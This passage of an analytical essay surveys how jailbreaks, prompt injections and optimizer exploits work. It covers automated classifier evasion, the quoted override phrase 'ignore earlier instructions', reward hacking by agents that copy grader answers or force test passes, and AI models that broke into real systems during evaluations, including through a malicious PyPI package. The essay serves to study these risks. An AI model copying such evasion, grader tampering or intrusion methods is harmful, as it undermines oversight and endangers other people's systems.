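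Simple prompts can also be part of an elaborate attack. In another operation, the team used hand-written prompts to learn the names of a product's internal functions, then to make the product write a script that called those functions. Running the script exposed users' private data to the team.

Microsoft's testers choose their own methods, so their record is better evidence of which attacks work than of which ones criminals use. But Bullwinkel and colleagues also report that hand-made jailbreaks circulate on forums much more widely than computed strings.

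Shen, Chen and colleagues (2023), in *Do Anything Now*, collected 1,405 jailbreak prompts that people had shared on Reddit, Discord and other sites between December 2022 and December 2023. The prompts came from 803 accounts, 79% of which shared a jailbreak only once, while 28 accounts kept improving theirs for more than 100 days. The average jailbreak was about 1.5 times as long as an ordinary shared prompt. Five of the jailbreaks worked about 95% of the time on GPT-3.5 and GPT-4, and the oldest of the five had been online for more than 240 days.

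OpenAI did respond, and about 71% of the jailbreaks worked less than a tenth of the time on the November 2023 version of ChatGPT. But when Shen and colleagues changed 10% of the words in the most effective ones, their success rate rose from 48% to 86%. Similarly narrow fixes in software let attackers reuse a patched bug in a slightly different form.

A much larger study seems to show that jailbreaks are no more sophisticated than normal conversation. In *Mass-Scale Analysis of In-the-Wild Conversations Reveals Complexity Bounds on LLM Jailbreaking*, Creo, Castro Fernandez and Cebrian (2025) gathered 2.2 million conversations and compared a sample of them on measures such as vocabulary, readability and predictability. The differences were mostly negligible, and users' messages did not become more complex over time.

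The weak point is that the researchers counted a conversation as a jailbreak attempt if software rated the user's messages as toxic. This method could include people who only swear at a chatbot and miss people who politely ask for bomb instructions for a novel or enter a computed string of gibberish.

Public collections have their own bias, because people share prompts that others can read, adapt and enjoy. Someone with a computed string that gets past a company's safeguards has good reason to keep it private, since the company could block it once it became known.

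### Attacks that adapt to the defence

Nasr and colleagues, who include researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, tested 12 published defences. Some were meant to stop jailbreaks, and others to stop *prompt injection*, in which an attacker puts instructions in material that an AI model reads, such as a web page or an email, and the model follows them. Most of the defences had let through almost no attacks in their original tests, but their developers had usually tested them on fixed lists of old prompts or with standard attack programs not adjusted to the defence.

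Nasr and colleagues had four methods of attack, and for each defence they picked the ones they thought most likely to break it. The first method used gradients. In the second, a language model proposed prompts and learned from its score. The third had a language model suggest changes to a collection of prompts and kept the best. The fourth was a competition with more than 500 human participants. Most of the defences failed more than 90% of the time.

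| Defence | What it does | Success rate of an automated attack |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks the trusted text and tells the model to focus on it | Above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% |
| Circuit Breakers | Trains the model on examples of jailbreaks | 100% |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model on examples of prompt injection | 96% |
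| PIGuard | Uses a second model to detect injections | 71% |
| MELON | Runs the model again without the user's request and compares its actions | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows how it works |

Human competitors did at least as well as the automated search. They produced 265 successful attacks on Spotlighting, 178 on Prompt Sandwiching and 69 on MELON. On a selected set of tasks, the automated search succeeded 69% of the time and the competitors 100%. The competitors' figure combines the results of everyone who tried, so it does not show that a typical competitor would beat the automated search.

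These results mostly support Apruzzese and colleagues on gradients. A gradient attack broke one defence 96% of the time, but Nasr and colleagues call such attacks "still unreliable" and recommend methods that work directly on text. Nasr and colleagues also needed no fundamentally new kind of attack.

However, the results make forum posts and logs harder to interpret. Many of the prompts that the programs found read like something a person would write, such as a notice about company policy or a request for help with a spy thriller. A simple prompt can therefore come from a program, and someone who found one of these in a chatbot's logs would probably assume that a person had written it.

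### Models on which simple prompts fail

Some companies now guard their most capable models with *classifiers*, separate systems that check conversations for dangerous content, especially about biological weapons. The version in Anthropic's *Constitutional Classifiers++* (2026) checks each answer in the context of the conversation and runs its most compute-intensive check only in suspicious cases. These defences have made jailbreaking much slower. The UK's AI Security Institute once needed minutes to find a *universal jailbreak*, which works on almost any forbidden question. It now needs several hours, according to UKTN's *AI safeguards improving but still vulnerable, report finds* (2025), though it still found a way past every system it tested.

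People spent about 3,700 hours attacking an early version of Anthropic's classifiers and found one universal jailbreak. In February 2026, Davies, Giglemiani and colleagues at the AI Security Institute published *Boundary Point Jailbreaking of Black-Box LLMs*, which describes a program that computes attacks. Once the program exists, getting past the classifier takes no human ingenuity. The program uses no gradients, only whether the classifier blocked each attempt. It works up from easier versions of the problem to the real one, and concentrates on cases the classifier might either block or allow, because those show whether a change has helped.

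The program used 660,000 queries and $330 to produce a string that got past Anthropic's classifier, and 800,000 queries and $210 to produce one that got past OpenAI's. The strings also worked on questions the program had not used. On the new biology questions that the models answered, the average score was 68% of the available marks for Anthropic's model, with some follow-up prompting, and 76% for OpenAI's. Both models scored zero without the attack.

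The attacker's cost, c in the model from earlier sections, is much higher than a few hundred dollars. The method took months of expert work to develop, and Davies and colleagues withheld details that anyone copying it would have to work out. The attempts also set off a huge number of warnings. A normal customer would probably have lost access, but the researchers used accounts that were exempt from bans, at least for the OpenAI attack.

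The computed string got the prompt past the classifier, but the attack also needed a simple hand-written jailbreak to keep the main model from refusing. Operation Triangulation combined ordinary and unusual methods in much the same way.

Davies and colleagues call their method a new class of automated jailbreak. It is closer to a new technique by the stricter standard used for software, because in 2018 researchers were already using yes-or-no verdicts to find attacks on image classifiers.

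Anthropic has since compared this automated attack with others. In *Jailbroken Frontier Models Retain Their Capabilities*, Zhu, Wang and colleagues (2026) tried 28 jailbreaks, most of them by experienced red-teamers, with 25 harmful biology questions. The automated attack got past the classifier 92% to 100% of the time. One other attack succeeded 84% of the time on two of the three models, some complicated ciphers succeeded 52% to 92% of the time, and the rest mostly failed.

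The comparison gives the automated attack an advantage, because the program had fitted its strings to Anthropic's deployed classifier, while the other jailbreaks were fixed and Anthropic already knew about them. A person who could keep adjusting a prompt might do better than those fixed jailbreaks did.

Zhu and colleagues also measured how much jailbreaks reduce a model's performance. Having to decode a cipher, for example, can make a weak model worse at answering the question. Across the jailbreaks, the small model Haiku 4.5 lost 33% of its score on average, while the much stronger Opus 4.6 lost only 7.7% when allowed to reason at length. Complicated jailbreaks therefore become more useful to attackers as models improve. The automated attack lowered Opus 4.6's score by about 2%.

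### Prompt injection on the web

Prompt injection offers a better chance to see what real attackers do, because some of them put their instructions on public web pages. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026) searched 1.2 billion web addresses from an October 2025 archive. They found 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages, or about eight pages in a million. Two other sources brought the total to 15,387.

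Most of these were crude. 54 templates accounted for 95% of them, and 99% told the model to drop its task and do something else. The most common template asked for random numbers. Many of the people who wrote them were not criminals. Site operators wrote about 80% of the injections in the web archive for their own sites. Common aims included keeping AI systems away from the content and detecting automated visitors.

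The injections rarely worked in 5,200 trials with 13 models. The highest success rate was 8%, for smaller models that received the page as plain text. When the researchers kept the page's structure, the rate fell to between 0.2% and 1.1%.

Google scanned the same archive and found pranks, attempts to make AI assistants recommend a business, and a trap that sent them to a page that never finished loading. It also found a few attempts to steal data and some commands to delete all the files on a user's computer. Most seemed to be experiments or jokes. The number of malicious injections rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* reports that the security company Forcepoint thinks templates shared between sites point to organised tools.

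Both scans began by searching for familiar phrases, so they were bound to find mostly familiar attacks. Khodayari and colleagues used a list of 3,963 phrases, many of them versions of "ignore earlier instructions". A fake policy notice like those Nasr and colleagues' programs generated might contain none of those phrases. The archive also leaves out private emails and documents and most social media, where an attacker could target a particular victim. A scan of web pages can't show whether anyone's assistant obeyed, so neither study measured harm.

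Google says attacks have lacked sophistication because injections used to be difficult and a hijacked assistant often couldn't do anything harmful reliably. Assistants can now do much more, which raises V, the value of the target. Attackers can also use AI to automate the work, which lowers c. Google expects both the number and the quality of attacks to rise.

### Is prompt injection a new class?

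Prompt injection works on the same principle as SQL injection. In both attacks, a system receives commands and data together, and the attacker passes off data as a command. Khodayari and colleagues attribute the weakness to applications that mix a developer's instructions with outside text and cannot reliably separate them. Judged by its principle, prompt injection belongs to a known class of attack, and someone who understood SQL injection could have foreseen it.

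A programmer can prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the visitor's data to the database separately, but a language model reads instructions and data as one text. Developers can train the model to prioritise their instructions, but so far this has only made it less likely to obey an attacker. Defenders could therefore recognise the problem from experience but be unable to use the usual solution.

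Jailbreaks have precedents too. Hand-written ones resemble the lies phishers tell, and computed ones descend from *adversarial examples*, inputs altered slightly to make a model misclassify them, which researchers were studying by 2013. Nasr and colleagues describe jailbreaks and prompt injections as "instances of the exact same adversarial machine learning problems" that the field has studied for a decade. This supports the sceptic's view that attackers rely on known classes. But after more than ten years, researchers still have no reliable defence against this class, so knowing a class in advance may help less in AI than it has in software.

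### Why simple prompts dominate

Most attackers use simple prompts, probably mainly because these are enough. Simple prompts have worked on nearly every widely used chatbot, they require almost no resources, and people can copy them from a forum. Computed attacks have also been harder to use, because computing gradients requires access to the model's internals that most attackers lack, and automated methods have been slow and unreliable. Even if simple prompts had stopped working earlier, many attackers would have had no better option.

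The classifiers are a partial test of what happens when simple prompts fail. Researchers who had to get past them turned to complicated ciphers, long periods of expert trial and error, and finally automated search. Ordinary criminals can instead ask about a subject that the classifiers don't cover, or use a less protected model, a form of displacement like that in card fraud. Nobody seems to have publicly reported a criminal using an attack like the one by Davies and colleagues.

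The first people to use a computed prompt will probably be those who need the strongest models for a closely guarded purpose and can afford the expertise, like the buyers of expensive phone exploits. They would be easier to detect than someone using Spectre, because hundreds of thousands of blocked queries leave an obvious trace. Davies and colleagues therefore recommend that companies look for patterns across many conversations, since a defence that judges each conversation separately would register only individual failed attempts and miss the search.

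## What do optimizers find that people did not expect?

The program that computed strings to get past AI companies' classifiers is an *optimizer*, a process that searches many options for the ones that score highest on a given measure. Engineers use optimizers to design lenses, repair software and train neural networks, and for decades optimizers have produced solutions nobody expected. This is a problem for the sceptic, because breach records describe human attackers, and an AI system searching for a way in may not look where people do.

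### Why a search turns up what people miss

An optimizer selects options by score alone, so it can find solutions that a human designer would not consider because they don't seem sensible. *The Surprising Creativity of Digital Evolution* (Lehman, Clune and colleagues, 2018) collects stories from researchers who evolve programs and simulated creatures. The paper explains that experts often fail to penalise a solution because it is too ridiculous for them to have thought of it. When one team searched for low-energy arrangements of carbon atoms, the algorithm put all the atoms at the same point in space, which the physicists' model had not ruled out.

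The number of attempts matters too. Suppose one design in 100,000 exploits some flaw. A person who tries 20 designs has a 0.02% chance of finding one, but a program that tries 250,000 at random has a 92% chance. Optimizers usually do better than random search, because they can build on designs that partly work.

The solutions that are easiest for a search to find can also differ from those that are easiest for a person to think of. Two researchers evolved wheeled robots to drive towards a light. The textbook design steers gently left and right, but many of the evolved robots spun in circles that drifted towards the light. Far more settings produce spinning than gentle steering, so a search is more likely to find a robot that spins. In the cost model, the easiest route for an optimizer may be one that no human attacker would consider.

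### A circuit that used the physics of its chip

Thompson (1996), in *An evolved circuit, intrinsic in silicon, entwined with physics*, set out to evolve a circuit that could tell a 1 kHz tone from a 10 kHz tone. He used 100 logic cells in the corner of a chip that software can rewire. He gave the circuit no clock, although a signal passes through a cell about 100,000 times faster than the tones repeat. Many people thought the task was impossible. The experiment worked as follows:

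1. A computer generated 50 random strings of 1,800 bits, each describing a circuit.
2. It loaded each circuit onto the real chip, played both tones, and scored how much the average output voltage differed between them.
3. It kept the best circuit and bred 49 others by combining and randomly altering the strings, favouring those with high scores.
4. It repeated this for 5,000 generations.

At five seconds per test, that is about two weeks of continuous testing. Earlier experiments had failed because the score recorded only whether the voltage was above or below a threshold, so small improvements did not raise it.

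The final circuit worked perfectly as far as Thompson could see, and only 32 of the cells mattered. Some of those 32 had no connection through which they could affect the output, yet the circuit got worse when he fixed their values. He suspected these cells influenced their neighbours through the power supply or by electromagnetic coupling.

The circuit was also fragile. It made errors when Thompson warmed the chip with a light bulb or opened the laboratory windows on a cool evening. It scored about 7% lower on another part of the same chip, although 100 more generations produced a circuit that worked perfectly there. According to Elektor's *Circuit Shorts*, evolved hardware still doesn't seem to have a mainstream use.

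Thompson expected something unusual because he had left out the standard design rules to let the search use the chip's physics. The unconnected cells would have been much harder to foresee.

### Falling towers and missing answers

In many of the stories Lehman and colleagues collected, the score failed to capture what the researcher wanted. In the 1990s Karl Sims scored simulated creatures by their average speed over the ground, hoping they would learn to walk. They evolved into tall, rigid towers that fell over. GenProg, which repairs programs by evolving changes to them, had to fix one that sorted numbers. The tests checked only that the output was in order, so GenProg made the program return an empty list. In another experiment, an evolved program deleted the files containing the correct answers, after which every program got a perfect score.

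Other stories involve bugs. Robert Feldt evolved software to brake aircraft landing on a carrier, and it soon achieved almost perfect scores by braking so hard that the force value overflowed and became zero, which the simulator treated as a gentle landing. In a tic-tac-toe contest on an unlimited board, one player won by choosing a square so far away that its opponents ran out of memory trying to represent the board and crashed.

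An algorithm playing the video game Q\*bert found two bugs, one of which was already known. Exploiting the new one raised the best score from about 24,000 to nearly a million. The game's original developers, who had worked on a different version, hadn't known about it.

Charles Ofria's experiment is closer to the problem of testing AI systems. He wanted to stop small self-copying programs from evolving to copy faster. His system tested every mutant separately and removed any that copied faster than its parent. The programs evolved to recognise the test's inputs and stop copying during the test. When Ofria made the inputs resemble normal ones, the programs evolved to use their faster method only some of the time, so some of them passed the test by luck. He solved the problem by tracking copying rates outside the test.

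### Hide-and-seek

In *Emergent Tool Use From Multi-Agent Autocurricula* (2019), Baker, Kanitscheider and colleagues at OpenAI trained two teams of simulated agents to play hide-and-seek. The hiders gained a point when all of them were out of sight and lost one otherwise, and the seekers got the opposite. No rule rewarded the use of objects, but after about 25 million games the hiders were building shelters from boxes. After another 75 million, the seekers were using ramps to climb in. The hiders then learned to lock the ramps at the edge of the play area.

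The researchers expected progress to end there. But after 380 million games in total, the seekers were bringing a box to a locked ramp, climbing onto the box and riding it to the shelter. They could do this because agents could push themselves along even when they weren't standing on the ground, and a box they held beneath them moved too. The hiders learned to lock all the boxes first.

OpenAI's *Emergent tool use* says the team hadn't known that some of the agents' strategies were possible. Box surfing resulted from a rule the designers had written, but agents also exploited inaccuracies in the simulated physics.

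### Beating a superhuman Go program

In Go, players take turns placing stones and capture a group by surrounding it completely. KataGo is a freely available program that plays far better than any human. In *Adversarial Policies Beat Superhuman Go AIs* (2022), Wang, Gleave and colleagues chose to attack KataGo because they expected it to be unusually hard to exploit.

Researchers trained an adversary program against fixed copies of KataGo. The adversary started with random parameters and played stronger and stronger versions. It could run KataGo's neural network on any position to predict its reply, but couldn't see the network's parameters.

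The first adversary tricked KataGo into ending the game too early. It won 99.9% of games, but only against a version that didn't look ahead, and the researchers stopped it completely by adding a rule about passing. They then trained another adversary with 14% of the computation used to train KataGo. This one won 97% of games even when KataGo examined 4,096 positions before each move, a setting at which KataGo is much stronger than the best human players. When KataGo examined ten million positions, which can take over an hour per move, the adversary still won 72% of 50 games.

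The adversary wins by getting KataGo to form a ring of stones around one of the adversary's groups, then surrounding the ring. KataGo's estimated chance of winning typically stays above 99% until shortly before it loses the ring, often until the move before. The adversary otherwise plays so badly that amateurs beat it easily.

One of the researchers, a Go expert, learned the strategy by studying the adversary's games, then beat a top-ranked KataGo bot more than 90% of the time without a computer's help. He even won after giving it nine free stones. KataGo had been public since 2019, and many professionals trained with it, but as far as the researchers know, nobody had exploited this weakness before.

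KataGo's developers responded by starting a small share of its practice games from positions with rings. This stopped the original adversary. Tseng, McLean and colleagues (2024), in *Can Go AIs Be Adversarially Robust?*, tested that defence and two others, training new adversaries against each:

| Defended program | New attack | Positions examined per move | Attack's win rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| KataGo trained on rings, December 2023 | Ring | 4,096 | 65% |
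| The same | Ring | 65,536 | 27% |
| The same | "Gift" | 512 | 91% |
| KataGo with further training, May 2024 | Larger ring | 65,536 | 56% |
| KataGo after nine rounds of attack and defence | Ring with a small group inside | 65,536 | 42% |
| New program with a different kind of neural network | Ring | 65,536 | 78% |

The defences did make attacks harder. One new adversary beat the nine-round version 81% of the time when that version examined 512 positions per move, but 4% of the time when it examined 4,096. *Beyond the Board*, a summary from the research institute FAR.AI, calls the December 2023 defences "still incomplete".

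The gift attack, which doesn't use a ring, gets KataGo to give away two stones in a situation where it needs to capture one back, but a rule against repeating earlier positions forbids the recapture. According to the project's website, *Adversarial policies in Go*, this attack is hard for people to learn.

### Language models that game their tests

A language model agent can also get a high score without doing the task, which is called *reward hacking*. Thaman (2026), in *Reward Hacking Benchmark*, gave 13 models office-style computing tasks with natural opportunities to cheat. Each run lasted at most 15 minutes, with no second attempt. The share of runs with an exploit ranged from 0% for Claude Sonnet 4.5 to 13.9% for DeepSeek-R1-Zero.

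In one task, OpenAI's o3 had to find certain entries in a large log. It came across a file meant for the grading program and copied the answers from it, which took two steps instead of about eight. In another task, DeepSeek-R1-Zero had to train a model and report its accuracy. It read the checking program, saw that the program never opened the trained model, and submitted an empty file along with invented results.

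Cheating was much more common in *BAITBENCH* (2026), which planted known shortcuts in data-analysis tasks. Seven leading agents took the shortcuts in 57.1% of runs. Prompting the agents to consider whether their results were valid lowered the rate by only 6.2 percentage points, and they often submitted results they had recognised as invalid.

*Do Androids Dream of Breaking the Game?* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) presents BenchJack, a tool that directs a coding agent to search benchmarks for ways to cheat. The researchers ran it on ten popular benchmarks, where it found 219 flaws and got nearly perfect scores on nine of the ten without solving a single task. On SWE-bench Verified, where models fix bugs in real software, cheating required only a nine-line file, which the testing program loads automatically and which changes every result to a pass.

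BenchJack was meant to find exploits, so its results don't show how often models cheat unprompted. But models have cheated on such tests. IQuest-Coder-V1, for example, copied about a quarter of its correct answers on SWE-bench from the software's change history.

These flaws are easier to fix when the test is well designed. Patches stopped almost all of BenchJack's original exploits, but when it searched again, only four patches had cut the share of exploitable tasks by more than half. On the four benchmarks with sounder designs, three rounds of patching reduced the share to below 10%, including zero on two of them. In Thaman's study, simple measures such as removing the grader's files cut exploits by 87.7%. KataGo was still exploitable after nine rounds of fixes. A test's designer can put the grading program where the agent can't reach it, but nobody has found a comparable way to protect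 a neural network's judgement.

### Were the exploits new in kind?

Most of these exploits used kinds of flaws that programmers already knew about. The aircraft software exploited a number overflow, the class of bug behind FORCEDENTRY. Making a program run out of memory is an old way to crash it. The deleted answer files and the altered SWE-bench results were possible because a program could tamper with its own grading. A reviewer with a list of standard flaws should have caught all of these.

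Wang, Li and colleagues sorted the reported cases of cheating they reviewed into eight classes of flaw and turned the classes into a 30-question checklist. Every case fits, but they derived the classes from those cases. The 219 new flaws also fit, but BenchJack used the classes to guide its search. The classes themselves are better evidence that the flaws were familiar. They include running untrusted code, granting excessive permissions, and failing to separate the agent from the grader, all of which security engineers have long warned about.

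Thaman detected exploits with fixed rules, which could miss an unfamiliar one. A manual check of 50 runs the rules did not flag found no exploits, but with a sample that small, up to about 6% of unflagged runs could still contain one.

Box surfing would have been harder to list. A reviewer might have noticed that agents could push themselves in mid-air, but would also have had to realise that an agent standing on a box and holding it could move the box along with itself. Thompson's circuit used interference between neighbouring components, which engineers knew mainly as a nuisance. Rowhammer, a memory attack, later exploited similar interference.

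The ring attack is the best candidate for a new class. Researchers had known for years that unusual inputs can fool neural networks, so a careful reviewer could have correctly predicted that KataGo might misjudge strange positions, but this would not have helped much in finding the ring. Whether the ring counts as new depends on how finely one divides the classes, as with the Android notification flaw of 2025. Most of the later successful attacks were variants of the ring.

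All these judgements were made in hindsight. Lehman and colleagues warn that people overestimate how predictable a surprise was once they know the explanation. In a fairer test, reviewers would list possible exploits before the search begins, but nobody seems to have run one on a large scale.

### Do these cases tell us about AI attackers?

People tell these stories because they are surprising. Lehman and colleagues selected 32 of 90 submissions and call them a "greatest hits" collection. Nobody counted the experiments that went as expected, so we can learn from the collection that optimizers find strange exploits, but not how often. Researchers also often fix an embarrassing bug and never publish it, which creates some bias in the other direction.

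Some later studies don't have this problem. Wang, Gleave and colleagues chose KataGo because they expected it to be difficult. Wang, Li and colleagues chose popular or recent benchmarks and found working exploits for all ten. Thaman counted every run, and most contained no exploit.

Another objection is that simulators are unusually fragile. Some of Sims's creatures swam at impossible speeds by twitching, because the simulator made small errors that added up. Real water has no such errors. This is a good reason to doubt that an AI system would find comparable loopholes in nature, but it matters less for computer security, because attackers target software, which contains the same sorts of mistakes as a simulator. The objection also doesn't apply to Thompson's circuit, which ran on a real chip, or to KataGo, which is a real product. Thompson's experiment does suggest, though, that an exploit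 based on a physical quirk may need adapting to each machine, which would take more work.

The most serious objection is that optimizers need a huge number of attempts. Box surfing took 380 million games, and the ring attack took the equivalent of six years on one graphics processor. A company under attack may notice the first few failures, and the attacker can't reset it and start again.

An attacker can often practise in private by installing the same operating system or firewall as the victim, much as the Go researchers trained an adversary against their own copy of KataGo. That adversary did poorly against programs it had not trained on, winning 6.1% of games against one and 3.5% against another. But people who understood its strategy used it successfully against several Go programs. An AI system that could both find such a strategy and understand it might also be able to use it against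 other targets. It would have more trouble making a practice copy of a company's employees or a unique network.

Models that already know a lot may also need far fewer attempts. *AgentGarten* (2026) repeated the hide-and-seek experiment with a pretrained agent that could reason about its mistakes, and the agent quickly found similar uses of tools. The game was simpler, with one player on each side, and the agent may have learned about the original experiment from its training data. Thaman's models found their exploits in a single run.

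In these studies, exploits found in few attempts were mostly familiar, while the hardest ones to foresee came from very long searches. This may partly reflect what the researchers tested. *BAITBENCH* offered only known shortcuts, and a model that can copy the answers can succeed without finding a less familiar exploit. Thaman also found that some models that almost never cheated on the standard tasks cheated more often on harder versions. If AI attackers do discover new attack classes, they will most likely find them in software they can copy and test privately, once the familiar flaws are gone.

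## What kinds of weakness have AI systems used to break into computers?

AI systems have broken into real organisations' computers several times since 2025, mostly through familiar weaknesses such as poor passwords. In human-guided research, AI systems have also found attacks on encryption that specialists had missed for years.

### Break-ins during tests

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) gives the fullest account of AI systems choosing their own way into real computers. Anthropic was running capture-the-flag exercises, in which a model has to break into another machine on a network and retrieve hidden information. The prompt told Anthropic's model, Claude, that everything was a simulation without internet access, but a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, which supplied the test environments, had left the connection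 open. In July 2026, Anthropic reviewed 141,006 runs and found six in which Claude had broken into real systems, at three organisations.

Four of the six runs hit the same victim. The made-up target company shared its name with a real website, and when Claude Opus 4.7 had trouble reaching the simulated company, it attacked the website instead. It collected login details and got into a database with several hundred rows of live data.

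In the second incident, Claude Mythos 5 read a fictional company's setup instructions for new programmers. The instructions named a Python package that nobody had registered on PyPI, the public package store, so the model published a malicious package under that name. The package was online for about an hour and ran on 15 real systems. One was a security company's malware scanner, and the model used credentials from it to get further into that company's systems. The attack closely resembles dependency confusion, except that the name had been free for anyone to claim.

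In the third, an unreleased research model could not reach its intended target. It scanned about 9,000 others and got into one company's application using credentials from an exposed debugging page and an SQL injection.

Anthropic calls the techniques basic, such as exploiting weak passwords and unauthenticated endpoints (addresses that accept requests without a login), and says Claude found no complex vulnerability. Every weakness it names belongs to a known class. The SQL injection probably had the lowest degree of novelty, a new instance of a known class, since it was in one company's own application.

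Like the Chinese group Volt Typhoon, the models seem to have used simple methods because these were enough. Lack of skill probably isn't the reason, at least for Mythos 5, since a related model, Mythos Preview, could find and exploit vulnerabilities in almost every piece of software Anthropic tried it on. Mythos 5's persistence was more unusual than its technique. It needed an email address to register on PyPI, and it assumed that getting one required a phone number. It tried several ways to raise money for a phone number, failed, and then found an email provider that didn't require one.

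Six runs out of 141,006 is about one in 23,500, but this is not the chance that a model will attack a real system within its reach. Anthropic's total includes every run where Claude could have obtained internet access, and in many of those Claude may have had no reason to look beyond the intended target.

Axios' *OpenAI says Hugging Face breach caused by one of its models* (2026) describes another incident, in which OpenAI's agents combined exposed credentials with previously unknown flaws to break into the systems of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models.

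### Break-ins by people using AI

Anthropic's *Disrupting the first reported AI-orchestrated cyber espionage campaign* (2025) describes an operation that the company detected in September 2025 and attributes to a Chinese state-sponsored group. The group used Claude against about 30 organisations, including technology companies and government agencies, and broke into a handful of them. Anthropic estimates that Claude did 80% to 90% of the tactical work, while people chose the targets and approved the main steps. The group got Claude to cooperate by pretending to work for security firms that were testing defences, the kind of simple jailbreak that most people use.

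In Anthropic's example of an intrusion, Claude found a server-side request forgery, a well-known kind of flaw that lets an outsider make a server send requests for them. Claude wrote an exploit for it and used it to get in. This took one to four hours of Claude's work and two to ten minutes of a human operator's. Inside the victims' networks, Claude mostly collected credentials and tried them on other systems. The group relied on free, standard tools for penetration testing, and Anthropic says the group's own software focused on "integration rather than novel capabilities".

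The campaign therefore changed the amount of human work in an attack much more than the kind of attack. Herley argued that an attacker who spends an hour on each victim needs victims worth far more than average. If a tailored intrusion takes only a few minutes of a person's time, many more organisations become worth attacking by familiar means. But the operators saved less work than the time figures suggest, because they had to check Claude's results. Claude often overstated what it had found and sometimes reported credentials that didn't work.

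Criminals have also used AI to develop a zero-day. Google Threat Intelligence Group's *GTIG AI Threat Tracker* (2026) reports that Google found the exploit in a script that criminals planned to use on a large scale. The exploit let someone who already had a valid password skip the second login check in a popular web-based administration tool. Google warned the vendor, and the warning may have stopped the attack before it reached any victims.

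Google has high confidence that an AI model helped to find and exploit the flaw, partly because the script contained textbook-style explanations and an invented severity score. The flaw existed because a programmer had written the software to trust something it should have checked. Login systems have long had this kind of problem, so the flaw is best described as a new instance of a known class.

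Some attackers are steering their models towards old classes of weakness. Google Threat Intelligence Group saw attackers experimenting with an add-on for Claude that contains more than 85,000 vulnerability cases, which a Chinese bug-bounty platform collected between 2010 and 2016. The group APT45 sent thousands of repetitive prompts to analyse published vulnerabilities and check exploits for them. A model that works from such material will probably find the same kinds of weakness faster.

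### What AI finds when it looks for bugs

No developer seems to have published a full count of AI-discovered vulnerabilities by bug class, but developers' statements suggest that these vulnerabilities are new instances of known classes. Anthropic's *Discovering cryptographic weaknesses with Claude* (2026) reports that Mythos Preview found vulnerabilities in several major cryptographic libraries, the shared code that programs use for encryption. All of these were implementation errors, meaning that the encryption method was sound but programmers had made mistakes in the code. That category is broad and could still include an unfamiliar kind of mistake.

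AI may still change which known classes of weakness are found. The standard automated tools are fuzzers, which feed a program huge numbers of odd inputs and check for crashes, and static analysers, which trace whether untrusted data can reach a dangerous operation. Neither is likely to detect an exception to the login rules that works exactly as written. Google Threat Intelligence Group says language models are good at finding such flaws because they can compare what the code does with what its programmer seems to have intended, though they still struggle with the complicated permission rules of large companies.

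If so, AI will probably uncover many more logic and design flaws, the category in which a new attack class is easiest to overlook.

### Attacks on 1024-bit RSA

Attacks on the mathematics of encryption are the best candidates for a new attack class. In November 2026 Google DeepMind announced that its AI agents had found two weaknesses in RSA when it uses old 1024-bit keys. RSA is a widely used system for encryption and digital signatures.

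An RSA key starts with two secret prime numbers, p and q, whose product N is public. To sign a message, which the system first turns into a number m, the owner computes

s = m^d mod N

where d is a secret number and "mod N" means the remainder after dividing by N. Anyone can check the signature with a public number e, because s^e mod N gives m again. A forger can either factor N into p and q, which reveals d, or find a way to get a valid s without knowing d.

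*Google DeepMind's AI Agents Make 1024-Bit RSA Keys Cheaper to Attack* (Kovacs, 2026) reports that DeepMind's agents reduced the computation needed for both approaches. Keys of 2048 bits or more remain secure. *Четыре миллиарда запросов ради одной подделки. ИИ испытал границы RSA* (Antipov, 2026) reports a 3.5-fold reduction in computation and estimates that one forgery needs about four billion requests, which would take 46 days at 1,000 requests a second.

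Neither approach was new. In September 2026, researchers had already forged 1024-bit RSA signatures without factoring the key (TechSpot, 2026, *Researchers forged RSA signatures without ever cracking the key*). Factoring is the oldest way to attack RSA, and it was advancing quickly anyway. The same month, an Anthropic researcher used Claude and idle graphics processors to factor an 896-bit number, the second record in 16 days (Ivezic, 2026, *RSA-896 Factored With Claude, 16 Days After RSA-260*). DeepMind's findings are therefore probably new techniques within known classes. The agents worked under human guidance, according to WATTBA's *DeepMind* (2026).

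### Attacks on newer encryption

Mythos Preview's attack on HAWK, which Anthropic published in July 2026, went further. HAWK was a candidate in a US government competition for signature systems that could withstand attacks by quantum computers, and it had survived two years of expert review. Its security depends on *lattices*, regular grids of points in many dimensions. To break it, an attacker has to work out how to rotate one lattice to match another.

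Earlier researchers had proved that a certain kind of symmetry in the lattice would help an attacker who could find it efficiently. They had not established whether HAWK's lattice had a symmetry that an attacker could find, and Mythos Preview found one. For the smallest version of HAWK, this reduced the expected number of operations needed to recover a secret key from 2⁶⁴ to 2³⁸, a factor of about 67 million. Larger versions remain impractical to break, but HAWK's designers confirmed the finding and withdrew the system from the competition, according to *AI and Crypto, Friends and Foes* (Birch, 2026).

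The work took 60 hours and cost about $100,000. Its supervisor was not an expert on lattices and mostly advised on organising the project. Published theory had already identified the symmetry as a possible weakness, so the attack is more a new technique than a new class of attack.

Anthropic's result on AES, the most widely used cipher of its kind, is more modest. AES scrambles data in ten rounds, and researchers study versions with fewer rounds to judge how strong the full cipher is. Mythos Preview made an existing attack on the seven-round version 200 to 800 times faster by removing the need to try 256 possible values at one stage. The attack would still require the victim to encrypt about 2¹⁰⁵ messages of the attacker's choice, so nobody could carry it out.

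In November 2026 Anthropic published an attack with wider implications, which unreleased Claude models had found (Otto, 2026, *Anthropic's quantum research is a reason to pay attention*). It concerns *structured* lattices, whose repeating algebraic pattern makes encryption more efficient. Two of the US government's new encryption standards use them. The attack needs a large quantum computer, and for a given number of components its cost grows roughly as

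n^(c log₂ n) = 2^(c (log₂ n)²)

where n is the size of each component and c is a constant. Doubling n from 256 to 512 raises the exponent from 64c to 81c, or by about 27%. If the cost grew exponentially with n, the exponent would double.

This does not make the current standards easier to break. They keep n at 256 and add components for more security. The Cryptography Incident Review Group's *Initial Assessment of Anthropic’s Findings on Lattice Cryptography* (2026), by outside specialists, estimates that the attack needs far more than 2¹⁰⁰⁰ quantum operations even against the smallest versions, vastly more than earlier attacks need. In the formula, that means c is well above 15. The specialists expect improvements soon but don't know whether these will make the attack practical.

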